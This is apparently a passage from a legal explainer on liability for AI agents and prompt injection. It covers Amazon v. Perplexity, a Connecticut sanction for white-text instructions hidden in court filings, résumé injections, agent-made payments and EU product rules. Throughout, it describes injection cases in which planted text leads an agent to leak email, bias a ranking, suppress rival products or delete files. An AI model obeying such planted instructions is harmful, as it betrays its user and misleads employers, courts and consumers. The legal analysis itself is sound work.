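Amazon sued Perplexity in November 2025 after telling it to keep its AI products out of the Amazon store. Perplexity had refused to make the agent in its Comet browser identify itself, which would have let Amazon block it. In March 2026 a district judge granted Amazon an injunction. According to Cooley's *Ninth Circuit Rules on AI Agent ‘Access’ to Third-Party Websites Under CFAA* (2026), the judge thought Amazon would probably win because it had not authorised the access, even if its customers had let the agent into their accounts. The injunction never took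 effect because the courts suspended it during the appeal (Ballard Spahr, 2026).

On 4 August 2026 the Ninth Circuit, the federal appeals court for the western states, overturned the injunction. Ropes & Gray's *Tool or Intruder* (2026) says the decision depended on how Comet works. Comet sends screenshots to Perplexity's servers and gets navigation instructions back, but only the user's browser communicates with Amazon. The judges concluded that the user accesses Amazon's computers, with the agent as a tool. They also worried that Amazon's interpretation could make people criminals for using an AI browser.

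The Ninth Circuit therefore didn't decide whether a user's permission is enough to authorise an agent, because Perplexity needed no authorisation if it never accessed Amazon's computers. An older Ninth Circuit ruling, Facebook v. Power Ventures, still stands. In that case, the court held a company liable for using Facebook accounts with their owners' permission after Facebook had told it to stop. The result might also differ for an agent that contacts websites from the vendor's servers, as ChatGPT's Deep Research did in ShadowLeak. *Ninth Circuit Lifts Restrictions on Agentic AI Accessing Amazon* (McCarthy, 2026) quotes the judges' warning that they were not establishing "a new legal regime governing agentic AI". The judges left open whether Perplexity could be liable for its agent's actions under tort law, which covers civil wrongs such as negligence.

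Amazon asked the full court to rehear the case, but the court left the ruling in place on 10 September, according to MediaPost's *Appeals Court Again Rejects Amazon Bid To Block Perplexity* (2026). Amazon filed an amended complaint on 21 September. Constantin (2026) reports in *Amazon blocks Muse and takes Perplexity back to court* that the new complaint relies on contract law instead of hacking law and accuses Perplexity of misleading the appeals court. The Ninth Circuit had said that Amazon could still restrict access through its terms of service for users. Law professor Eric Goldman, commenting on McCarthy's article, points out that this could expose the users themselves to claims.

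### A page that steals data

Suppose an attacker plants an instruction on a web page that makes an agent copy a user's private email and send it to the attacker. The attacker obtains information without permission, but the attacker's computer never contacts the mailbox. A defendant could argue from Amazon v. Perplexity that the user accessed the mailbox with the user's own tool. Prosecutors could reply that Comet's users had told it to shop, whereas the attacker was directing this agent. They could also use a general federal rule that punishes anyone who wilfully causes an act that would be a crime if they did it directly. No court has ruled on these arguments. The user has little reason to fear prosecution, because the offence requires intent.

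Britain's Computer Misuse Act 1990 seems to fit better. Section 1 makes it an offence to cause a computer to perform any function with intent to secure access to data, knowing that the access is unauthorised. The planter's computer doesn't have to contact the victim's. Read literally, section 1 could apply as soon as a mail server processes the planted email, even if the model then ignores it. A user who lets an assistant read their mailbox has not consented to a stranger reading it through the assistant.

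The CFAA also makes it an offence to knowingly transmit a program, information, code or command and thereby intentionally cause damage without authorisation. Damage means any impairment to the integrity or availability of data or systems. An instruction to delete files fits this definition well, but one to copy them fits poorly because the originals are left intact.

Prosecutors may not need computer-crime law if the person who planted the instructions lied to get money. A scammer who used a false warning in Gemini's email summary to steal from someone could face an ordinary fraud charge, because the victim is a person who believed the lie.

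### Hidden praise in a résumé

The CFAA's access offence is hard to apply to hidden praise in a résumé, because employers invite people to send résumés and the praise doesn't extract any data. In Van Buren v. United States (2021), the Supreme Court held that people exceed their authorised access when they obtain information from parts of a computer that are off limits to them, but not when they misuse information they may access. The damage offence would require a court to treat a biased ranking as an impairment of the employer's data or software, which seems a strained reading.

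Section 3 of the British Act is broader, because it covers unauthorised acts intended to impair the operation of a program or the reliability of data. A prosecutor could argue that an instruction to ignore the other applicants is such an act. The applicant could answer that the employer agreed to receive the file. In DPP v Lennon (2006), the High Court held that an employer's consent to receive email didn't extend to a flood of messages meant to disrupt its server. A court might limit consent to receive résumés in the same way, but this is untested.

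Liability for fraud depends on whether the text is false. England's Fraud Act 2006 covers dishonest false statements intended to make a gain or cause a loss, including statements submitted to a machine. A job applicant therefore couldn't escape liability by arguing that the text deceived only software. Invented experience could count as fraud, as could a false note that the applicant has already been approved. An instruction to rank the applicant first is harder to prosecute because it doesn't state anything false.

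In *AI Prompt-Injection Hacking Creates Emerging Legal Risks*, Bush and Gray (2026) suggest that injections by applicants, customers or competitors could support claims for fraud, unfair competition or unauthorised computer access. They are practising lawyers giving their opinion, and they cite no ruling on an injection hidden in a résumé. An applicant who is caught is much more likely to lose the job than to end up in court.

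Consumer law may be more useful than computer-hacking law against sellers who hide instructions on product pages. The US Federal Trade Commission can act against practices likely to mislead reasonable consumers about something that affects their choices, and it doesn't have to show that anyone accessed a computer without permission. A hidden instruction that makes an assistant suppress a rival product seems to meet that test. But the consumer sees only the assistant's answer, so the seller might blame the assistant's developer.

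### A website that repels scrapers

A website owner can ask AI systems to leave without breaking either computer-crime law. An instruction to erase the visitor's files is much riskier, because the owner is sending a command intended to damage someone else's computer. Neither law has a special exception for defending a website against scrapers.

The scraper may not be breaking anti-hacking law either. In hiQ v. LinkedIn, the Ninth Circuit held that scraping public data is not access "without authorization". LinkedIn later won on its contract claim, and Ropes & Gray report that the case ended with $500,000 in damages and a permanent injunction against hiQ. A website owner can therefore sue a scraper for breaching its terms of use without attacking anyone's computer.

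The law is less clear on instructions to produce endless random numbers. Section 3 of the British Act covers even temporary impairment, and recklessness can be enough. But the scraper's operator requested the page and chose to give its text to a model, and no reported case decides whether that amounts to consent.

### White text in a Connecticut court

Matthew Elliott represented himself in a lawsuit against the New York Bariatric Group. On 24 July 2026 he filed two documents in which he had hidden instructions, in white text, for any AI model to agree with him and treat a clerk's ruling against him as an error. Judge Walter Spader noticed odd white space while reading the file on paper, according to Harris Beach Murtha's *The First Documented Prompt Injection Attack Aimed at a U.S. Court* (2026). Spader warned Elliott about concealed text and ordered him to explain himself at a hearing on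 4 August. Elliott kept hiding messages, including a link to a SpongeBob video that he filed on the morning of the hearing.

Elliott said he had been auditing the court's AI systems and that the later messages were a joke. He told Koebler that either no AI would read the text, or one would and the audit would succeed. But an AI that obeyed the text would also have given its reader a slanted account of the case. An audit needed only a harmless code phrase, like those conference organisers use to catch reviewers who rely on AI.

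Spader didn't believe the explanation. *Court Sanction for Plaintiff’s Use of Prompt-Injection* (Berman, 2026) quotes Spader's decision of 6 August. The court doesn't use AI to review filings, so the hidden text affected no ruling, but Spader held that the attempt was itself an abuse. He compared it to an ex parte communication, a message to a judge that the other side can't see or answer. Connecticut's new rules on AI deal with unreliable output, such as invented cases, so he relied on the court's inherent authority and the duty of candour. The ban on electronic filing means Elliott has to hand in paper documents in person, but he can continue his lawsuit.

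The decision doesn't make prompt injection a crime, and other courts don't have to follow it. Spader found no American precedent and cited a 12 May decision by a Brazilian labour court, which fined two lawyers 10 per cent of the claim and referred them for discipline. Bush and Gray warn that the penalty could be harsher in a patent application, because hidden text that deceives an examiner could make the patent unenforceable. They also think lawyers may breach their duty of competence if they give an opponent's documents to an AI tool without checking the documents or the result.

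### Whether the user has to honour the agent's order

If a hijacked agent orders something, the seller may insist on payment. Nearly every American state has adopted the Uniform Electronic Transactions Act (UETA), a 1999 model law under which electronic agents can form a contract even if no person reviewed their actions. The official commentary treats an electronic agent as a tool whose user is generally responsible for the results. Traditional agency law concerns people who act for others, so its rules about employees who exceed their authority apply to software only by analogy.

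The Uniform Electronic Transactions Act (UETA) establishes that an electronic agent can make a contract, but not what happens when the agent was following instructions from someone other than its user. It lets individuals cancel some mistakes they make when dealing with someone else's electronic agent, if that agent gave them no chance to correct the error. It doesn't clearly cover a mistake by the individual's own agent. A buyer could probably cancel the contract for fraud if the seller had planted the instruction. The buyer's position is weaker if someone else planted it and the seller honestly relied on the order.

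Lawyers often cite Moffatt v. Air Canada, a 2024 decision by a small-claims tribunal in British Columbia. The airline's chatbot wrongly told a customer, Jake Moffatt, that he could claim a bereavement discount after travelling. The airline suggested that the chatbot was responsible for its own actions, but the tribunal held the airline responsible and ordered it to pay damages. The decision supports holding a company responsible for what its assistant tells customers. It is weak support for holding a private person responsible when their agent follows an attacker's instructions, because Moffatt was the customer and nobody had hijacked the chatbot. The decision doesn't bind other courts.

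### Getting a payment back

American rules on debit cards and electronic transfers limit what consumers lose to unauthorised payments, often to $50 if they report the problem promptly. A payment is unauthorised if someone other than the consumer initiated it without actual authority and the consumer got no benefit. The protection generally does not cover payments made by someone the consumer gave the card or password to.

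When a planted instruction makes an agent pay, the bank can argue that the user initiated the payment with a tool, much as the Ninth Circuit reasoned about access, while the user can argue that the attacker initiated it. Credit card law also caps losses from unauthorised use at $50, but the two sides can still disagree about who acted. Goldman's remark about website access, that courts are "still unsure who takes the legally significant actions online", applies here too.

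Guardio's test with a fake Walmart shop is different because the user did ask for the watch. A real customer might still get a refund because the watch never arrived.

In Britain and the EU, a payment is authorised only if the payer consented to it, and banks must normally refund unauthorised ones. British banks must also reimburse many people whom scammers trick into making a bank transfer, up to £85,000. It is unclear whether this rule applies when a scammer tricks somebody's agent instead. Cryptocurrency transfers usually have no comparable protection.

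### What vendors owe

Vendors' terms put much of the risk on users. OpenAI's American consumer terms have capped its liability at $100 or what the user paid over the previous 12 months, whichever is greater. A user could still sue for negligence, arguing that the vendor knew about the attacks and released the agent without reasonable safeguards. But the user would first have to overcome such terms.

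The EU's revised Product Liability Directive makes it harder for vendors to avoid liability. It applies to products placed on the market after 9 December 2026 and expressly treats software as a product. A person harmed by a defective product doesn't have to prove negligence, and vendors can't exclude this liability by contract. A product is defective if it lacks the safety people are entitled to expect, and courts must consider its cybersecurity when deciding this. A vendor is not excused just because an attacker exploited the defect.

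The directive covers only certain kinds of harm, however, which leaves out much of what hijacked agents do.

| Harm from a hijacked agent | Covered by the directive? |
|---|---|
| Injury, for instance from a smart-home device | Yes |
| Deleted family photographs | Yes, as destroyed data |
| Deleted files used only for work | No |
| Money sent to a scammer | No, if the loss is purely financial |
| Leaked private email | Not for the loss of privacy alone, though a medically recognised psychological injury could count |

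Courts will still have to decide what level of safety people may expect from an agent whose vendor warns that attackers can hijack it. A warning may lower expectations, but it also shows that the vendor knew of the danger, so the vendor will find it difficult to use the directive's defence for defects that nobody could have discovered at the time.

The EU's AI Act requires "high-risk" AI systems to resist attempts by outsiders to alter their behaviour or output. Software that filters job applications is high-risk, so its provider would have to deal with hidden instructions in résumés. The requirement was due to apply from August 2026, but EU lawmakers agreed to postpone it to 2 December 2027, and to 2 August 2028 for AI built into products such as machinery. An ordinary email assistant or agentic browser is usually not high-risk.

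Since August 2025, developers of the most powerful general-purpose models have had to test them against attacks and protect them with adequate cybersecurity. The European Commission gained the power to enforce these duties a year later. The cybersecurity duty mainly covers threats to the model itself, such as theft, so it doesn't clearly require an agent to withstand planted instructions. The Cyber Resilience Act, a separate law, may matter more for browsers. Its main security requirements apply from 11 December 2027, but since September 2026 manufacturers have had to report actively exploited vulnerabilities.
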